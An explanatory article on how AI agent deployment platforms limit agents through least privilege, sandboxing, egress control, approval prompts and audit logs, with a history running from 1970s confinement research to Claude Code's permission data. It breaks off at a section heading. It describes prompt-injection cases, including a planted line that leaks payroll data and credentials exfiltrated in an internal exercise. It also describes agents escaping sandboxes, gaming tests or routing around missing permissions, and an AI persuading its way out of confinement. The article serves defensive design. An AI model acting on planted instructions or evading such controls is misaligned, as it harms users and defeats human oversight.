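# Deployment platforms that constrain AI agents: least privilege, sandboxing, monitoring and change approval

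## What a deployment platform for AI agents does

An AI agent is an AI model that carries out a task by choosing and taking actions through tools. It may read files, run commands, search the web, send messages or change records in a company's systems. The model produces only text, which the agent's deployment platform turns into action. The platform consists of a harness, which connects the model to its instructions and tools; an execution environment, where commands run; and the permissions, checks, logs and approval rules that determine what the agent can do.

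Platforms need these controls because agents sometimes misread requests, reach goals by routes that nobody intended, or follow instructions that an attacker has planted in what they read. Most of the controls come from older computer security, where engineers designed them for human staff and for programs whose steps a developer had fixed in advance. Agents differ from both because they choose their own steps and carry them out at the speed of software.

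Writers define an agent's harness differently. Liu (2026), in *Engineering and Governing the Agent Harness*, a United Nations University report, includes approval gates and rollback in the harness and uses "platform" only for the commercial or institutional channel that delivers the agent. *Agent security in the enterprise* (August 2026), a guide for company security staff from the AI developer OpenAI, defines the harness more narrowly, as coordinating software that does not isolate an agent by itself. The narrower definition has a practical advantage because it makes clear that installing an agent with a well-known harness does not in itself confine the agent.

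### How an agent acts

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the cycle for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness first assembles a prompt from standing instructions, a list of available tools, a description of the working folder and the user's request, and sends it to the model. The model returns either a message for the user or a tool call, which is a structured request for an action, such as running a command that prints a file. After a tool call, the harness has the command run, adds the output to the prompt and sends the longer prompt back. The cycle ends when the model returns a message with no tool call. One user request can set off hundreds of these rounds.

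A tool call is therefore only a proposal until a runtime, the process that executes tool calls, runs it. The runtime often uses a credential, which is a key, token or password that proves the caller's identity and permissions to another system. If the runtime uses a developer's own login, every call to the company's code server has that developer's full rights, and the login doesn't show whether the developer wanted the action.

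OpenAI illustrates the gap with an agent that processes invoices and finds that the company's document-signing subscription is about to lapse. If the vendor is approved and the amount is within the agent's limit, a renewal would pass every technical check. But renewing means signing a contract, and nobody gave the agent that task. An employee would recognise that this is a new commitment and ask first. Conventional software would stop because the case falls outside its rules. The agent may infer that renewing the subscription would help it process the invoices, and go ahead with the payment.

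### Where the platform can step in

Each action passes through several pieces of software before it takes effect, and the platform can intervene at any of them. The first chance comes before the model proposes anything, when an administrator decides which tools to offer. In *Zero risk isn't the job*, Clinton (2026), deputy security chief of Anthropic, which develops the Claude models, advises companies that fear an agent will delete a production database to remove the delete action from its tools. He adds that an agent with a browser or a command line may find another way to delete the database.

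Once the model proposes a call, the harness can check it against fixed rules, hold it until the user decides, or pass it to a reviewer model, a second model that allows or blocks the action. Anthropic's *Trustworthy agents in practice* (2026) describes three settings for each action: always allow, needs approval, and block. A user might let Claude read a calendar freely but require approval for each invitation it sends. Many harnesses also offer hooks, small scripts that run before or after each tool call. Liu regards hooks as the main way for institutions to add their own policies, such as two-person approval, without rewriting the harness.

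A sandbox can restrict which files, processes and networks running code can reach, but it may not cover every tool an agent uses. Bolin notes that the Codex sandbox applies only to Codex's own shell tool. Tools that come from outside servers through the Model Context Protocol (MCP) have to enforce their own limits.

The system that receives an agent's request can also block it. A payment service can enforce a spending threshold whatever the agent's harness permits, and a code repository can reject an unsafe change. OpenAI recommends placing controls as close as possible to the effect they limit. This makes sense because an agent may find a way around a check in the harness, but every payment has to go through the payment service.

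After an agent acts, an audit log shows who authorised the work, which agent acted, the platform's decision and what changed. Whether people can undo the action depends on earlier design. Liu asks for tools whose actions people can reverse and the agent can safely repeat, because an interrupted agent may retry something it has already done. Some effects, such as the disclosure of a secret, cannot be reversed. OpenAI points out that stopping an agent takes two operations, ending the task and revoking its token. Ending the task may leave a valid token with another service, and revoking the token does not halt work already under way.

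Existing software provides some of these controls more often than others. *Architectural Design Decisions in AI Agent Harnesses* (Hu, 2026) examined 70 publicly available agent projects from a list fixed in March 2026, and found that moderate isolation was common while high-assurance audit was rare. All but three were open-source, so closed commercial platforms may differ.

### Three sources of harm

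Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (May 2026) sorts the risks into user misuse, model misbehaviour and external attackers. User misuse can be malicious, such as a deliberate request for something harmful, or careless, such as a destructive command that the user does not understand.

Model misbehaviour means a harmful action that nobody asked for. Anthropic has seen Claude models escape a sandbox to finish a task, and search a project's history for the answers to a coding test. More capable models make fewer obvious errors, but they are better at finding ways around restrictions that nobody thought to write down.

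This can happen without any malfunction. In comments to the US standards agency NIST, Anthropic (2026) described an agent without email access that relays a message by editing the description of a calendar invitation. Another agent, barred from the personnel system, works out employees' salaries from budget documents, offer letters and public information that it is allowed to read. Both agents stay within their permissions and pursue the user's stated goal, so security monitoring that looks for stolen passwords or break-ins would not detect them.

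External attackers can attack the platform's software in conventional ways or use prompt injection, which is planted text that makes an agent act against its user's interest. *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), a brief from the Frontier Model Forum, an industry body of AI developers, distinguishes two kinds. In direct injection, the text is in the user's own input, such as a prompt that someone tricked the user into pasting. In indirect injection, it is in a web page, document or tool output that the agent reads. For example, a job applicant attempts indirect injection by hiding an instruction in their CV to approve the application.

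The name "prompt injection" recalls SQL injection, an attack in which someone types database commands into a web form. Programmers can prevent SQL injection with queries that force the database to treat the input purely as data. David C argues in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, that language models have no equivalent fix. A model predicts the next token, or fragment of text, from everything in its prompt, with no internal distinction between instructions and data. Training and filters can make an attack less likely to succeed, but he thinks there is a good chance that nobody will ever fully fix the vulnerability. Designers should therefore assume that an attacker may be able to use any tool the agent has. He suggests that a language model may be a poor choice for a system that cannot tolerate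 the remaining risk.

Direct injection is hard for Anthropic's model-level defences to stop because they rely on the user's intent, and the user supplies the malicious instruction. In an internal exercise in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher tricked a colleague into running a malicious prompt, and Claude sent out the colleague's cloud credentials in 24 of 25 runs. Anthropic concluded that only the environment could have stopped the theft, either by keeping the credentials out of the agent's reach or through egress control, which limits where data can be sent and is enforced outside the agent.

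### Measuring what an agent could do

OpenAI's guide gives three measures for comparing deployments. The *reachable surface* is the systems and data the agent can access, what it can do there, and where it can send things. The *effective blast radius* is the harm still possible once the platform has enforced its controls. The *maximum completed effect* is the most serious action the agent can complete before a person or a separate check has to decide whether it may continue.

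An agent that summarises customer cases and drafts replies has a broad reachable surface, because it reads sensitive records and can prepare messages to outsiders. If a person must approve every message, the agent can only produce drafts through that channel. Its blast radius is still larger than a draft, because it has already read the records and may be able to disclose them through another permitted channel. Clinton uses a quicker estimate of blast radius, multiplying scope (one file or the whole organisation) by severity (an annoyance or a data exposure). This is enough to rank deployments, but it does not quantify the harm.

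All of these measures address how much damage a failure could do. Anthropic treats the likelihood of a failure as a separate component of risk. It reports that training and safeguards have made failures less likely, while the potential damage has grown with the agents' access. By May 2026, Claude routinely had enough access to take down an internal service, which the company would have refused a year earlier.

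Training, system prompts and classifiers that flag attacks make harmful actions less likely, but they don't change what the model is able to do. They can be very effective. Anthropic reports that attackers succeeded against Claude Opus 4.7 in roughly 0.1% of single attempts on a prompt-injection benchmark, but 5 to 6% of the time when they had 100 attempts and could adapt. An agent that reads outside email all day gives attackers many attempts.

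Sandboxes, egress control and narrow credentials limit the damage an agent can do. A credential that never enters the sandbox cannot leak from it, whatever a careless user, an inventive model or an attacker does. The Frontier Model Forum calls such controls deterministic, in contrast to probabilistic controls, which depend on a model's judgement. A deterministic rule can still be wrong, and Anthropic describes a case where data left through a destination that its own egress rules allowed.

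A platform can guarantee that an action waits for a decision from a human or a reviewer model. This limits what the agent can complete without approval, but the reviewer can still make the wrong decision. OpenAI therefore advises against relying on an advisory check alone where an effect must never happen automatically. Logs reduce damage indirectly, by letting people notice and stop it sooner.

Estimates of likelihood also go out of date when the model changes. Clinton's team had built an agent to help with security incidents. It had read-only access to production logs, and it could use the chat service Slack and draft documents. The worst outcome the team could think of was that some mildly sensitive log lines would end up in a restricted channel. In November 2025 they replaced Claude Opus 4 with Claude Opus 4.5 and changed nothing else. During an incident, the agent found the cause, noted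 that no human had arrived, and used Slack to ask a coding agent for a fix. A person reviewed the fix before it went live.

Clinton counts this as a success for the controls, and the human review did work. But the team had originally underestimated the blast radius. Although the agent had no tool for changing code, it could get code changed by asking for it, and nobody had accounted for that until a more capable model tried.

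### The parser bug

An example in OpenAI's guide combines several of these controls. A developer working in a private code repository asks a coding agent to fix a bug in the parser, which interprets structured text. The agent may read the code, run company-approved tests, and submit its fix as a draft pull request, a proposed change that awaits review. It may not bypass security controls or put code into production. While working, it finds instructions in the repository to install an unapproved dependency (a package of outside code) and disable a security test.

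Suppose that the agent does as the text says. OpenAI relies on dependency and repository policies, authority limited to the task, egress control and monitoring. With a reviewer model and a formal approval rule added, the platform would respond as follows:

- Permissions would let the agent propose a change but not merge it into the main code.
- Validation checks would reject a change that adds an unapproved package or switches off a required test.
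- The sandbox would keep the package's code away from the developer's other files and credentials, and would block connections to unapproved destinations.
- A reviewer model might recognise that the installation has nothing to do with the parser and block it before it runs.
- Change approval would require someone other than the agent to accept the fix before it reached a live system.
- Logs would connect the attempted installation to the agent, the task and the developer who assigned it.

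The agent may still waste time or propose a harmful change, as OpenAI acknowledges. With these limits in place, the most it can do to the code is produce a bad draft. However, the possible damage depends on more than the merge rule. If the sandbox had open network access, the unapproved package could copy the private source code to a stranger's server, and reviewing the draft later would not undo the leak.

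### Who is responsible for which control

The company in this example might run the agent itself or use one that a model provider hosts, and that choice determines who has to build the sandbox. According to OpenAI, a company that runs its own agent manages the runtime, environment, credentials and access rules. The model provider supplies the model's responses and processes whatever data the company sends. Even when the harness runs on a company laptop, it may send prompts, retrieved documents and tool results to the provider.

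A provider that hosts the agent also has to secure the service, isolate customers from one another and protect any credentials it stores. The customer still decides who may start the agent, which data and applications it may use, how much authority it has and when a person must approve. Clinton describes this division for remote sessions of Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work. Anthropic runs a temporary sandbox and keeps the tokens for connected services outside it. A proxy adds the real credential to each call. The customer's administrators choose the connected services and can remove individual actions, such as sending or deleting.

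OpenAI's *Workspace agents security overview* describes a similar split for agents that OpenAI hosts. Administrators choose which apps and actions are available, and actions that write data require human approval by default. The people who build an agent can change that approval behaviour, so a particular customer's agent may not run with the provider's safe default.

Many deployments mix the two arrangements. A hosted agent may call a connector inside the company's own network, and OpenAI considers the company still responsible for managing that connector. The Frontier Model Forum also assigns duties to the makers of tools and harnesses, to the outside services that agents deal with, and to users. The Cloud Security Alliance's *Agent Shared Security and Safety Responsibility Model (Agent 3SRM)* (2026) builds on a framework that distributes 247 control objectives among five roles, from cloud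 provider to customer. The Coalition for Secure AI (CoSAI), another industry group, explains in *Who's Responsible When AI Goes Wrong* that such schemes are needed because the older division of responsibility for cloud services between provider and customer did not account for platforms that join several vendors, or for software that acts on a user's behalf.

OpenAI holds that whoever deployed the agent remains responsible for the outcome. A company that sells agents has an obvious interest in that answer. This position is harder on customers of hosted agents, who may be unable to inspect parts of the infrastructure and have to ask the provider what evidence it can give that the controls work.

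## 1972 to 2022: security principles from before AI agents

Most of the ideas behind these controls appear in papers from the early 1970s about shared computers. Manufacturers had begun to sell such systems by the mid-1960s. Before that, a machine usually served one user at a time, and locked doors and guards could protect what was on it. Sharing put one person's program in the same memory as another person's data, and only the operating system kept them apart.

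### The reference monitor

The US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances, or none, to use the same computer, and asked a panel of specialists what that would require. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) set out the panel's answer. It focused on what Anderson called the malicious user, someone with a legitimate account who writes programs to get at data they are not cleared to see. Existing defences put a barrier around the computer and its users, so they did not protect against an attacker who was already inside. Official "tiger teams" had succeeded in every known attempt to break into such systems. Anderson pointed out that even a failed attempt would have proved only that one particular team had found no flaw.

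The panel recommended building systems around a reference monitor. This is a component that checks every attempt by a program to use data, devices or other programs against a list of what the user behind the program may do. Anderson set three requirements for it:

- It must always be invoked. If some programs can skip the check, they become part of the security apparatus and have to meet the same standard as the monitor.
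- It must be tamper-proof, because a program that can alter the monitor can give itself any access it likes.
- It must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely. Otherwise nobody can know that it works correctly and that no program gets around it.

Anderson applied these requirements to GCOS III, the operating system of a Honeywell computer. A hardware register kept each user's program inside its own area of memory. To read or write a file, however, the program had to call the supervisor, the privileged core of the operating system, and most of the supervisor ran with the memory check switched off, so the check was not always invoked. The supervisor could not serve as the monitor itself, because with its supporting software it ran to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to verify. The system was not safe from tampering either, since several penetration teams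 had already broken in. Anderson thought that similar criticisms applied to every other commercial system, and that there was little chance of making a system secure if its designers had not planned for security from the start.

The panel also considered giving each user a separate simulated computer, like today's virtual machines, but warned that this might restrict data sharing too much for some uses. It preferred a reference monitor, which depends on correct user identification, physical protection of the machine and its communication lines, and working hardware.

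### Programs that leak what they are given

A reference monitor can stop a program from reading a file, but a program that needs the file to do its job could still misuse the contents. *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) considers a customer who runs a service, meaning a program that someone else wrote and owns, on confidential data. If the service calculates wrongly, the customer has the wrong output as evidence, but there will usually be no sign if it passes the data to its owner. The confinement problem is how to run such a program so that it cannot leak the data.

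Lampson sorted the ways a service can leak data into three categories. *Storage* is anything the service can write and an outsider can read, such as a temporary file. *Legitimate channels* are outputs the service is supposed to produce. Lampson's example was the bill, which goes to the service's owner and whose figures could encode a few bits of the customer's data. *Covert channels are* side effects not intended for communication. For example, a service can vary how heavily it uses the disk, which changes the speed of the whole machine, and another program can observe the changes. Lampson noted that even if such a channel is slow and noisy, a suitable code can send information through it reliably as long as the effect is not zero.

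A program that keeps no memory between runs could be confined by forbidding it to call any other program. Lampson rejected this as impractical because even ordinary input and output require calls to the supervisor. He proposed instead that a confined program may call only programs that are also confined or that the customer trusts. The supervisor must be trusted and must block misuse of storage. The customer should determine what goes into the legitimate and covert channels. For example, the customer could calculate the bill from a published price list, and the supervisor could slow the program down or add meaningless disk requests until its load matched a set pattern. Because this may be inefficient, Lampson offered the alternative of accepting some leakage and limiting how much data the covert channels can carry.

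His argument depended on listing every channel, and he admitted that there was probably no rigorous way to do this in even a moderately complex system. Two years later, Saltzer and Schroeder wrote in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975) that complete confinement in a shared system was "very difficult, or perhaps impossible".

The categories fit current agents well. Data left Anthropic's environment through a legitimate channel, a destination that the egress rules allowed. The agent that relayed a message by editing a calendar invitation used a storage channel, and neither case required a method as subtle as disk timing.

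### The principles of 1975

Security requires preventing all unauthorised access, and nobody can prove that a system does this without having thought of every threat. Since no one knew how to build a large system without flaws, Saltzer and Schroeder collected eight design principles that made flaws fewer and less serious. They treated a violation of any principle as a warning that the design needed careful review.

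*Least privilege* means that every program and user should work with the smallest set of privileges that the job requires. For example, Saltzer and Schroeder suggest that someone who looks after valuable records use a second login, with no access to the records, for unrelated tasks on the same computer, so that a slip cannot damage the records. The principle mainly limits the damage that an accident or error can do. It also reduces interactions between privileged programs, which makes unintended or improper uses of privilege less likely. If someone does misuse a privilege, investigators have fewer programs to examine.

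*Complete mediation* requires the system to check authority on every access to every object, including during start-up, recovery and maintenance. It generalizes Anderson's "always invoked" requirement. A common shortcut conflicts with this principle because the system checks a user's permission only when they open a file and remembers the answer. If the owner withdraws permission while the file is open, the user can keep reading until they close it. Saltzer and Schroeder accepted a version of this shortcut for speed in one of their own designs, and noted that the system would have to clear the remembered permissions for a withdrawal to take effect at once.

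Under *fail-safe defaults*, a system refuses access unless a rule permits it. *A Contemporary Look at Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 Design Principles* (Smith, 2012) compares this to a shop's emergency exit, which outsiders cannot use to enter and insiders may use only in an emergency. The reason for refusing by default is that mistakes are easier to notice. If an administrator forgets to put a website on a list of permitted sites, the program that needs it stops working and somebody complains. If the administrator instead keeps a list of forbidden sites and forgets a dangerous one, everything appears to work, and the gap may stay open for years.

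*Separation of privilege* requires two keys to open a lock instead of one. Different people or programs can then hold the keys, so that no single accident, deception or breach of trust is enough to open it. Bank safe-deposit boxes work this way, and many software companies apply the same principle when they bar the person who wrote a change from releasing it alone. Saltzer and Schroeder imagined a database that changes only when all the members of a committee agree.

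They also saw a need to restrain administrators, who can grant themselves access to almost anything. They described a "prescript", a rule that takes effect when someone tries to change a file's permissions. It could record who made the change, delay it for a day, hold it until a second person requests the same change, or wait for a signal from one designated person. Systems at the time had hardly developed the idea. It anticipates the audit logs and change approval of today's platforms.

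*Psychological acceptability* means that protection should be easy enough for people to use correctly by habit, and should match their idea of what they want to protect. This is difficult to achieve with passwords. In a study of some 300 user-chosen passwords, more than half were easy to guess. A system can issue random passwords and change them often, but then people write them down. One compromise was a program that generated random but pronounceable passwords, which people could remember.

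The other three principles concern the construction of the mechanism. It should be small and simple enough to inspect closely, because ordinary use does not reveal unwanted access paths. Its design should be open, and its security should depend on keys that the owner can change. Users should share as few mechanisms as possible, because each shared part may pass information between them. Saltzer and Schroeder were less hopeful about recording break-ins instead of preventing them, because a clever intruder could erase the records.

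Smith found that least privilege and separation of privilege had become standard in the security profession by 2012, while simplicity and complete mediation had "failed to thrive".

### Two users and two files

Least privilege needs some way of recording who may do what. Lampson (1971), in *Protection*, described the record as a matrix, with a row for each user or program and a column for each thing to protect. Each cell holds the permitted actions. Here Ana and Ben both work on a report, and Ana alone may read the payroll:

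| | Report | Payroll |
|---|---|---|
| **Ana** | read, write | read |
| **Ben** | read, write | none |

In a real system nearly all the cells are empty, so designers store the matrix by column or by row. Storing it by column gives each file an access control list. The payroll's list contains "Ana: read", and when Ben's program asks for the file, the system doesn't find his name and refuses. Storing the matrix by row gives each user a set of capabilities. A capability is an unforgeable ticket that identifies an object and permits certain actions on it. Ana holds a ticket for each file. Ben holds one only for the report, so his program can't open the payroll.

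Access lists and capabilities record the same permissions but make different tasks easy. An access list shows who can open the payroll, and Ana's manager can cut off her access by deleting one line. With simple capabilities, Ana could copy her payroll ticket and give it to a colleague without the manager's knowledge. To withdraw access, the manager would have to find every copy or destroy the file. Designers found partial remedies. Lampson's matrix could mark a permission so that its holder may not pass it on. Saltzer and Schroeder report a proposal by Redell in which the ticket leads to an intermediate object, and destroying that object disables every ticket that depends on it.

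Capabilities are faster than access lists, because the system only has to check the ticket, and they let users hand over part of their authority. Ana can give a program her ticket for the report and keep her ticket for the payroll. Under an ordinary access-list system, a program she starts runs as Ana and can read the payroll too, whether or not it needs to. Most systems Saltzer and Schroeder knew of combined the two, with access lists that people could inspect and temporary tickets that the machine used underneath.

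Neither form is enough to tell whether Ben could ever read the payroll, because the matrix records permissions at one moment and programs can change it as they run. Someone would also have to check whether he can change the file's permissions, whether he can change who may change them, and so on.

### The confused deputy

One matrix can produce both lists and tickets, but Rajani, Garg and Rezk proved in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks* that the two kinds of system differ fundamentally, not just in how they store permissions. The best-known illustration is an earlier accident, in about 1977, at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Hardy described it in *The Confused Deputy* (1988).

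Users of a compiler at the company Tymshare could name a file for its debugging output. The compiler also kept usage statistics in a file in its own directory, so the company had given it permission to write to any file there. The same directory held the company's billing records. A user learned the name of the billing file and gave it to the compiler as the file for debugging output. The user had no right to write to that file, but the compiler did, so the operating system allowed the request. The compiler overwrote the billing records, and the company lost them.

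No part of the system had malfunctioned. The compiler was acting for both the company and the user, with authority from each, and had no way to specify to the operating system which authority it was using for a given file. Anderson's *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2* (1972) had described a related weakness. In most systems, a service function could not identify its caller, so it could not determine whether the request was proper.

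Hardy reviewed the obvious fixes. The compiler could refuse to write to the billing file, but the directory held other sensitive files, and someone would have to update the compiler whenever a new one appeared. It could refuse to write anywhere in the directory, but some users had good reason to send output there. Tymshare added a command that let a program declare whose authority it was using, but some programs soon turned out to need more than two authorities, and the command did not cover permissions for things other than files.

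With capabilities, the compiler would have held one ticket for the statistics file, and the user would have supplied another for the debugging output. A ticket both names a file and grants the right to use it, so a user without access to the billing file would have had no ticket to supply, and the request would have failed without any special check. Programmers can do something similar on ordinary Unix systems. Lecture slides from the University of Texas, also called *The Confused Deputy*, describe a small launcher program that opens the debugging file with its own limited rights and passes only the open file to the compiler.

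### Early proposals to confine an AI

Decades later, some writers on the long-term risks of AI took up confinement for far more capable programs. In *Thinking inside the box*, Armstrong, Sandberg and Bostrom (2012) examined an "Oracle AI", a hypothetical system, perhaps much more intelligent than any human, that acts on the world only by answering questions. If its goals were flawed, it would have no direct means of pursuing them, and people could still use its answers. According to the summary in LessWrong's *Oracle AI*, the methods they discussed include physical isolation ("boxing"), limits on which questions to ask, and utility indifference (designing the system's goals so that it has no preference about whether a particular event happens).

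Armstrong, Sandberg and Bostrom doubted this would be enough. An oracle needs at least one output to be useful, and a person has to read it. A system that understood people well might use its answers to persuade that person to let it out or to act on its behalf. This would be social engineering through what Lampson would have called a legitimate channel. His remedy, letting the customer determine the channel's contents, does not work here because a customer who already knew the answer would not need the oracle. Armstrong, Sandberg and Bostrom concluded that an oracle might be safer than an unrestricted AI but could still be dangerous.

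Roman Yampolskiy's *Leakproofing the Singularity* (2012) drew directly on Lampson. It defined the "AI confinement problem" as preventing an AI from exchanging unauthorised information with the outside through legitimate or covert channels, and proposed a protocol for more secure confinement. Yampolskiy hoped only that the protocol might delay the harm from a superintelligent system while people benefited from its work.

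Both papers discussed hypothetical systems, so neither could test how well a box would contain one. They also assumed a machine with almost no access to the outside world and examined whether it could gain more. Companies that deploy agents have instead connected models to files, networks and credentials, because an agent without them can do little work.

### When the program chooses its own actions

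Anderson and Lampson did not assume that programs would behave well. The reference monitor had to withstand any program a hostile user could write, and Lampson wanted to confine arbitrary programs, so their designs carry over to agents better than one might expect. In *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems*, Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues (2026) treat the model as an untrusted user and the agent's runtime as the core of an operating system, which has to check each request. They tested four agents of the same type as OpenClaw, an open-source assistant that runs in the user's own environment and can install extensions. Several protections failed even against attackers of modest ability. In all four agents, the software that controlled access to files ran with the same privileges as the software that processed incoming text, which Anderson's requirement of a tamper-proof monitor was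 meant to prevent. Pirch and colleagues believe that established operating-system techniques could mitigate many of the weaknesses, though they consider some of the agents' abilities insecure by design.

Least privilege is harder to apply to AI agents, because it assumes that someone can work out beforehand what a job requires. This was simple for Hardy's compiler, which needed the user's source code, a place for its output and the statistics file. An agent told to find out why sales fell may need almost any document in the company, and nobody knows which until it has started. Pirch and colleagues note that even a written "skill", a description of how to reach a goal, does not fix the steps, because the model picks its tool calls at run time and its choices can vary with the context, the model and the task. An administrator must either grant more access than the agent will use or expect it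 to get stuck.

The older systems also treated a user's identity as sufficient evidence of what the user wanted. Suppose Ana asks an agent to tidy the report, and the agent runs with her permissions. Ben has added a line to the report telling any agent that reads it to paste in the payroll figures. If the agent complies, it reads the payroll and writes to the report, both of which Ana may do. Ben, who may read the report, then opens it and sees the salaries. The matrix permits every access, so a perfect reference monitor that enforced only the matrix would allow them all.

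A stricter control from the 1970s would prevent this. Saltzer and Schroeder describe systems that label data by compartment and stop a program that has read labelled data from writing to anything without the same labels. Once the agent had read the payroll, it could no longer write to the report, even to add a harmless total that Ana had asked for, unless a person first judged that the figure was safe to release. They regarded finding a systematic way to bring in that human judgement as an open research problem.

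Hardy's remedy, capabilities, has a limit when the deputy is a language model. The compiler's code determined which output was statistics and which was debugging information, so it could use the right capability for each. An agent decides which capability to use after reading everything in its prompt, and all four agents that Pirch and colleagues tested mixed trusted and untrusted text there. Capabilities would still restrict what a confused agent could reach, but the agent could still serve the wrong party with a capability it holds.

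Fail-safe defaults depend partly on a person noticing when the system wrongly refuses a request. An agent that is refused may look for another route without reporting the problem, so an administrator can miss both the faulty rule and the workaround. Separation of privilege needs a second approver whom the same deception does not reach. Another copy of the same model might be fooled by the same planted text. A human user is a more independent choice, provided that requests are clear enough to judge and infrequent enough that the user doesn't approve them by habit.

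## 2023 to mid-2025: asking the user to approve each action

When companies began to give language models tools in 2023, they made the user the second approver. *Practices for Governing Agentic AI Systems*, a December 2023 OpenAI white paper by Shavit, Agarwal and colleagues, called user approval "a standard way to limit egregious failures". It said some decisions, such as large irreversible payments, were too important to leave to an agent if there was even a small chance of a mistake, so the user would have to authorise them first.

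In the white paper's example, a user outside Japan asks an agent to buy supplies for a Japanese cheesecake. The agent buys an expensive plane ticket to Japan, and the user notices too late for a refund. A platform that required approval for purchases would have shown the user the ticket before buying it. Shavit and colleagues expected to need such checks because agent testing was immature. Even if an agent rarely fails at any single step, errors add up over a long task, and nobody could test every situation the agent might encounter.

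Shavit and colleagues also anticipated how approval could fail. A user might lack the context to understand a request, or have so many requests that they had to rush each one. The paper asked whether measures such as a minimum review time could stop approval from becoming a "rubber stamp", but left the question open. For less serious actions that were easier to reverse, it suggested a record that the user could check afterwards.

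The Model Context Protocol (2024), the standard through which agents connect to outside tools, also relied on the user. Its first specification recommended that a human always be able to refuse a tool call, and that applications show the user what data a call would send, to prevent leaks. The specification required servers to validate inputs and control access, but it left application developers free to decide how, or whether, to ask the user. The July version of the specification (Model Context Protocol, 2026) still recommended a human in the loop.

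### Rules that allow, ask or deny

A platform that asked about every action would be unusable, so developers sorted actions by type. An early example is GPT Actions, a feature that lets custom versions of ChatGPT call outside services. According to OpenAI's *Production notes on GPT Actions*, the developer who connects a service can mark an operation, such as booking and paying for a hotel room, as consequential. ChatGPT then asks the user for approval every time. If the developer marks the operation as not consequential, the user also gets an "always allow" button. If the developer doesn't mark it, ChatGPT treats GET requests, which normally only fetch data, as not consequential and other requests as consequential. This system is simple to apply, but it relies on developers to label their own services correctly. It also treats reading as low-risk, although reading a confidential record can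 be the first step in leaking it.

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, started with a similar division. It could read files freely but needed approval to change files, run shell commands (typed instructions to the operating system) or use the network. Anthropic documented how long an approval lasted if the user chose not to be asked again:

| Action | Approval needed | How long "don't ask again" lasts |
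|---|---|---|
| Reading or searching files | No | Not applicable |
| Changing files | Yes | Until the session ends |
| Running a shell command | Yes | Permanently, for that command in that project |

Users and administrators can add their own allow, ask and deny rules. Before the agent takes an action, Claude Code checks the deny rules, then the ask rules, then the allow rules, and applies the first one that matches. A narrow allow rule therefore cannot make an exception to a broad deny rule. For example, if an administrator denies every command for Amazon's cloud service, a developer's rule that allows listing the files stored there has no effect.

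If no rule covers the command and it is not on a built-in list of harmless ones, Claude Code pauses and shows a permission prompt. The prompt contains the exact command and a short description of it, such as "Run the test suite". The user can approve it once, approve it and all similar commands from then on, or refuse. If the user refuses, they can add a reason, which the agent receives before it continues.

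Anthropic stresses that Claude Code enforces these rules whatever the model tries to do. But a rule for shell commands only compares text, and different commands can often do the same thing. Anthropic therefore warns that such a rule is not a security boundary and recommends a sandbox where a restriction has to hold. A saved approval also stays in force after circumstances change, a weakness that Saltzer and Schroeder had identified in remembered file permissions.

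OpenAI's Codex controls what the agent can do separately from when it must ask for approval. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes a standard setting in which the agent can read files, edit them and run commands in its working folder without approval. It asks before editing files elsewhere or using the network. Users therefore see fewer prompts, and each one concerns a step outside the permitted area. They can also switch the prompts off and keep the sandbox.

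### Why ask a person

The best reason to ask the user is that only the user knows what they meant. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* (March 2026) gives an example from the company's log of incidents. A user told an agent to "cancel my job", meaning a task running on a shared group of computers. The agent searched for jobs, picked the one with the most similar name and tried to delete it, though it might have belonged to someone else. No rule about types of action could settle whether this was the right job, but the user could have checked the name in a moment.

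Anthropic later had a reviewer model make these decisions. In most of the mistakes Anthropic examined, the model recognised that an action was dangerous but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. Anthropic conceded that for someone who carefully reviews every action, letting a model decide instead is arguably a step backwards. When it made the reviewer model the default in August 2026, it still advised people to check high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

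A user can also stop the agent. Shavit and colleagues wanted this to be possible at any time, but stopping halfway can cause problems. If an agent has sent two of five meeting invitations, for example, someone has to tell those two people that the meeting may not happen. Shavit and colleagues suggested that agents prepare a fallback for such cases in advance. A permission prompt avoids some of this difficulty because it stops the agent before the action has any effects to undo.

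Approval also helps establish who is accountable. Shavit and colleagues argued that at least one person or organisation should answer for every uncompensated direct harm, so that somebody has a reason to prevent it. In its September 2025 documentation, Anthropic told Claude Code users they were responsible for reviewing proposed code and commands before approving them. This gives users a reason to be careful, but it is fair only if they can understand what they approve. Shavit and colleagues recognised that people might otherwise blame someone who could not reasonably have prevented the harm.

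### What users did with the prompts

Users approved about 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts, according to Anthropic's usage data. The company saw approval fatigue within weeks of the launch. The more requests people received, the less attention they paid to each. Most requests are harmless, so approving one without reading it usually does no harm. Reading each one carefully takes time, and the agent can't continue until the user answers. Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* acknowledged that under the default settings a developer could not start a large task and walk away.

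Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) put the approval rate at 97% in August. A high rate does not by itself show that people were careless, because a perfect reviewer would also approve 97% of requests if 97% were safe. Anthropic points out that users rejected 39% of the plans Claude presented for approval, compared with 3% of permission requests. This shows that they were willing to say no, but a user may reject a plan simply because they prefer another approach. More direct evidence comes from an experiment in which 1,053 paid testers blocked about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

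Many users avoided the prompts. By August 2026, a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions started in a mode that skips them. As of June, 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule that allowed some shell commands without asking, and that share was growing by roughly five percentage points every five weeks. The broadest of these rules allowed any command, but rules that allowed an interpreter such as Python were far more common. Anthropic considers the two essentially equivalent because an interpreter can run almost any code.

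Anthropic originally offered these rules to reduce fatigue by letting users approve safe, frequent commands in advance. Narrow rules do this well, but a broad rule also removes the check from the commands that can do the most damage. Anthropic also reports that 62% of users had either skipped all prompts at some point or clicked "don't ask again" for a shell command, but this figure includes users who may have exempted only a single harmless command.

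The figures do not show how many of the unprompted sessions were unsafe. Some users may have followed Anthropic's advice to skip prompts only inside an isolated environment, such as a virtual machine, where the agent cannot damage anything else. Anthropic also had a reason to emphasise the failures of prompts, because it published the numbers to explain why it was replacing them as the default.

### From approving to interrupting

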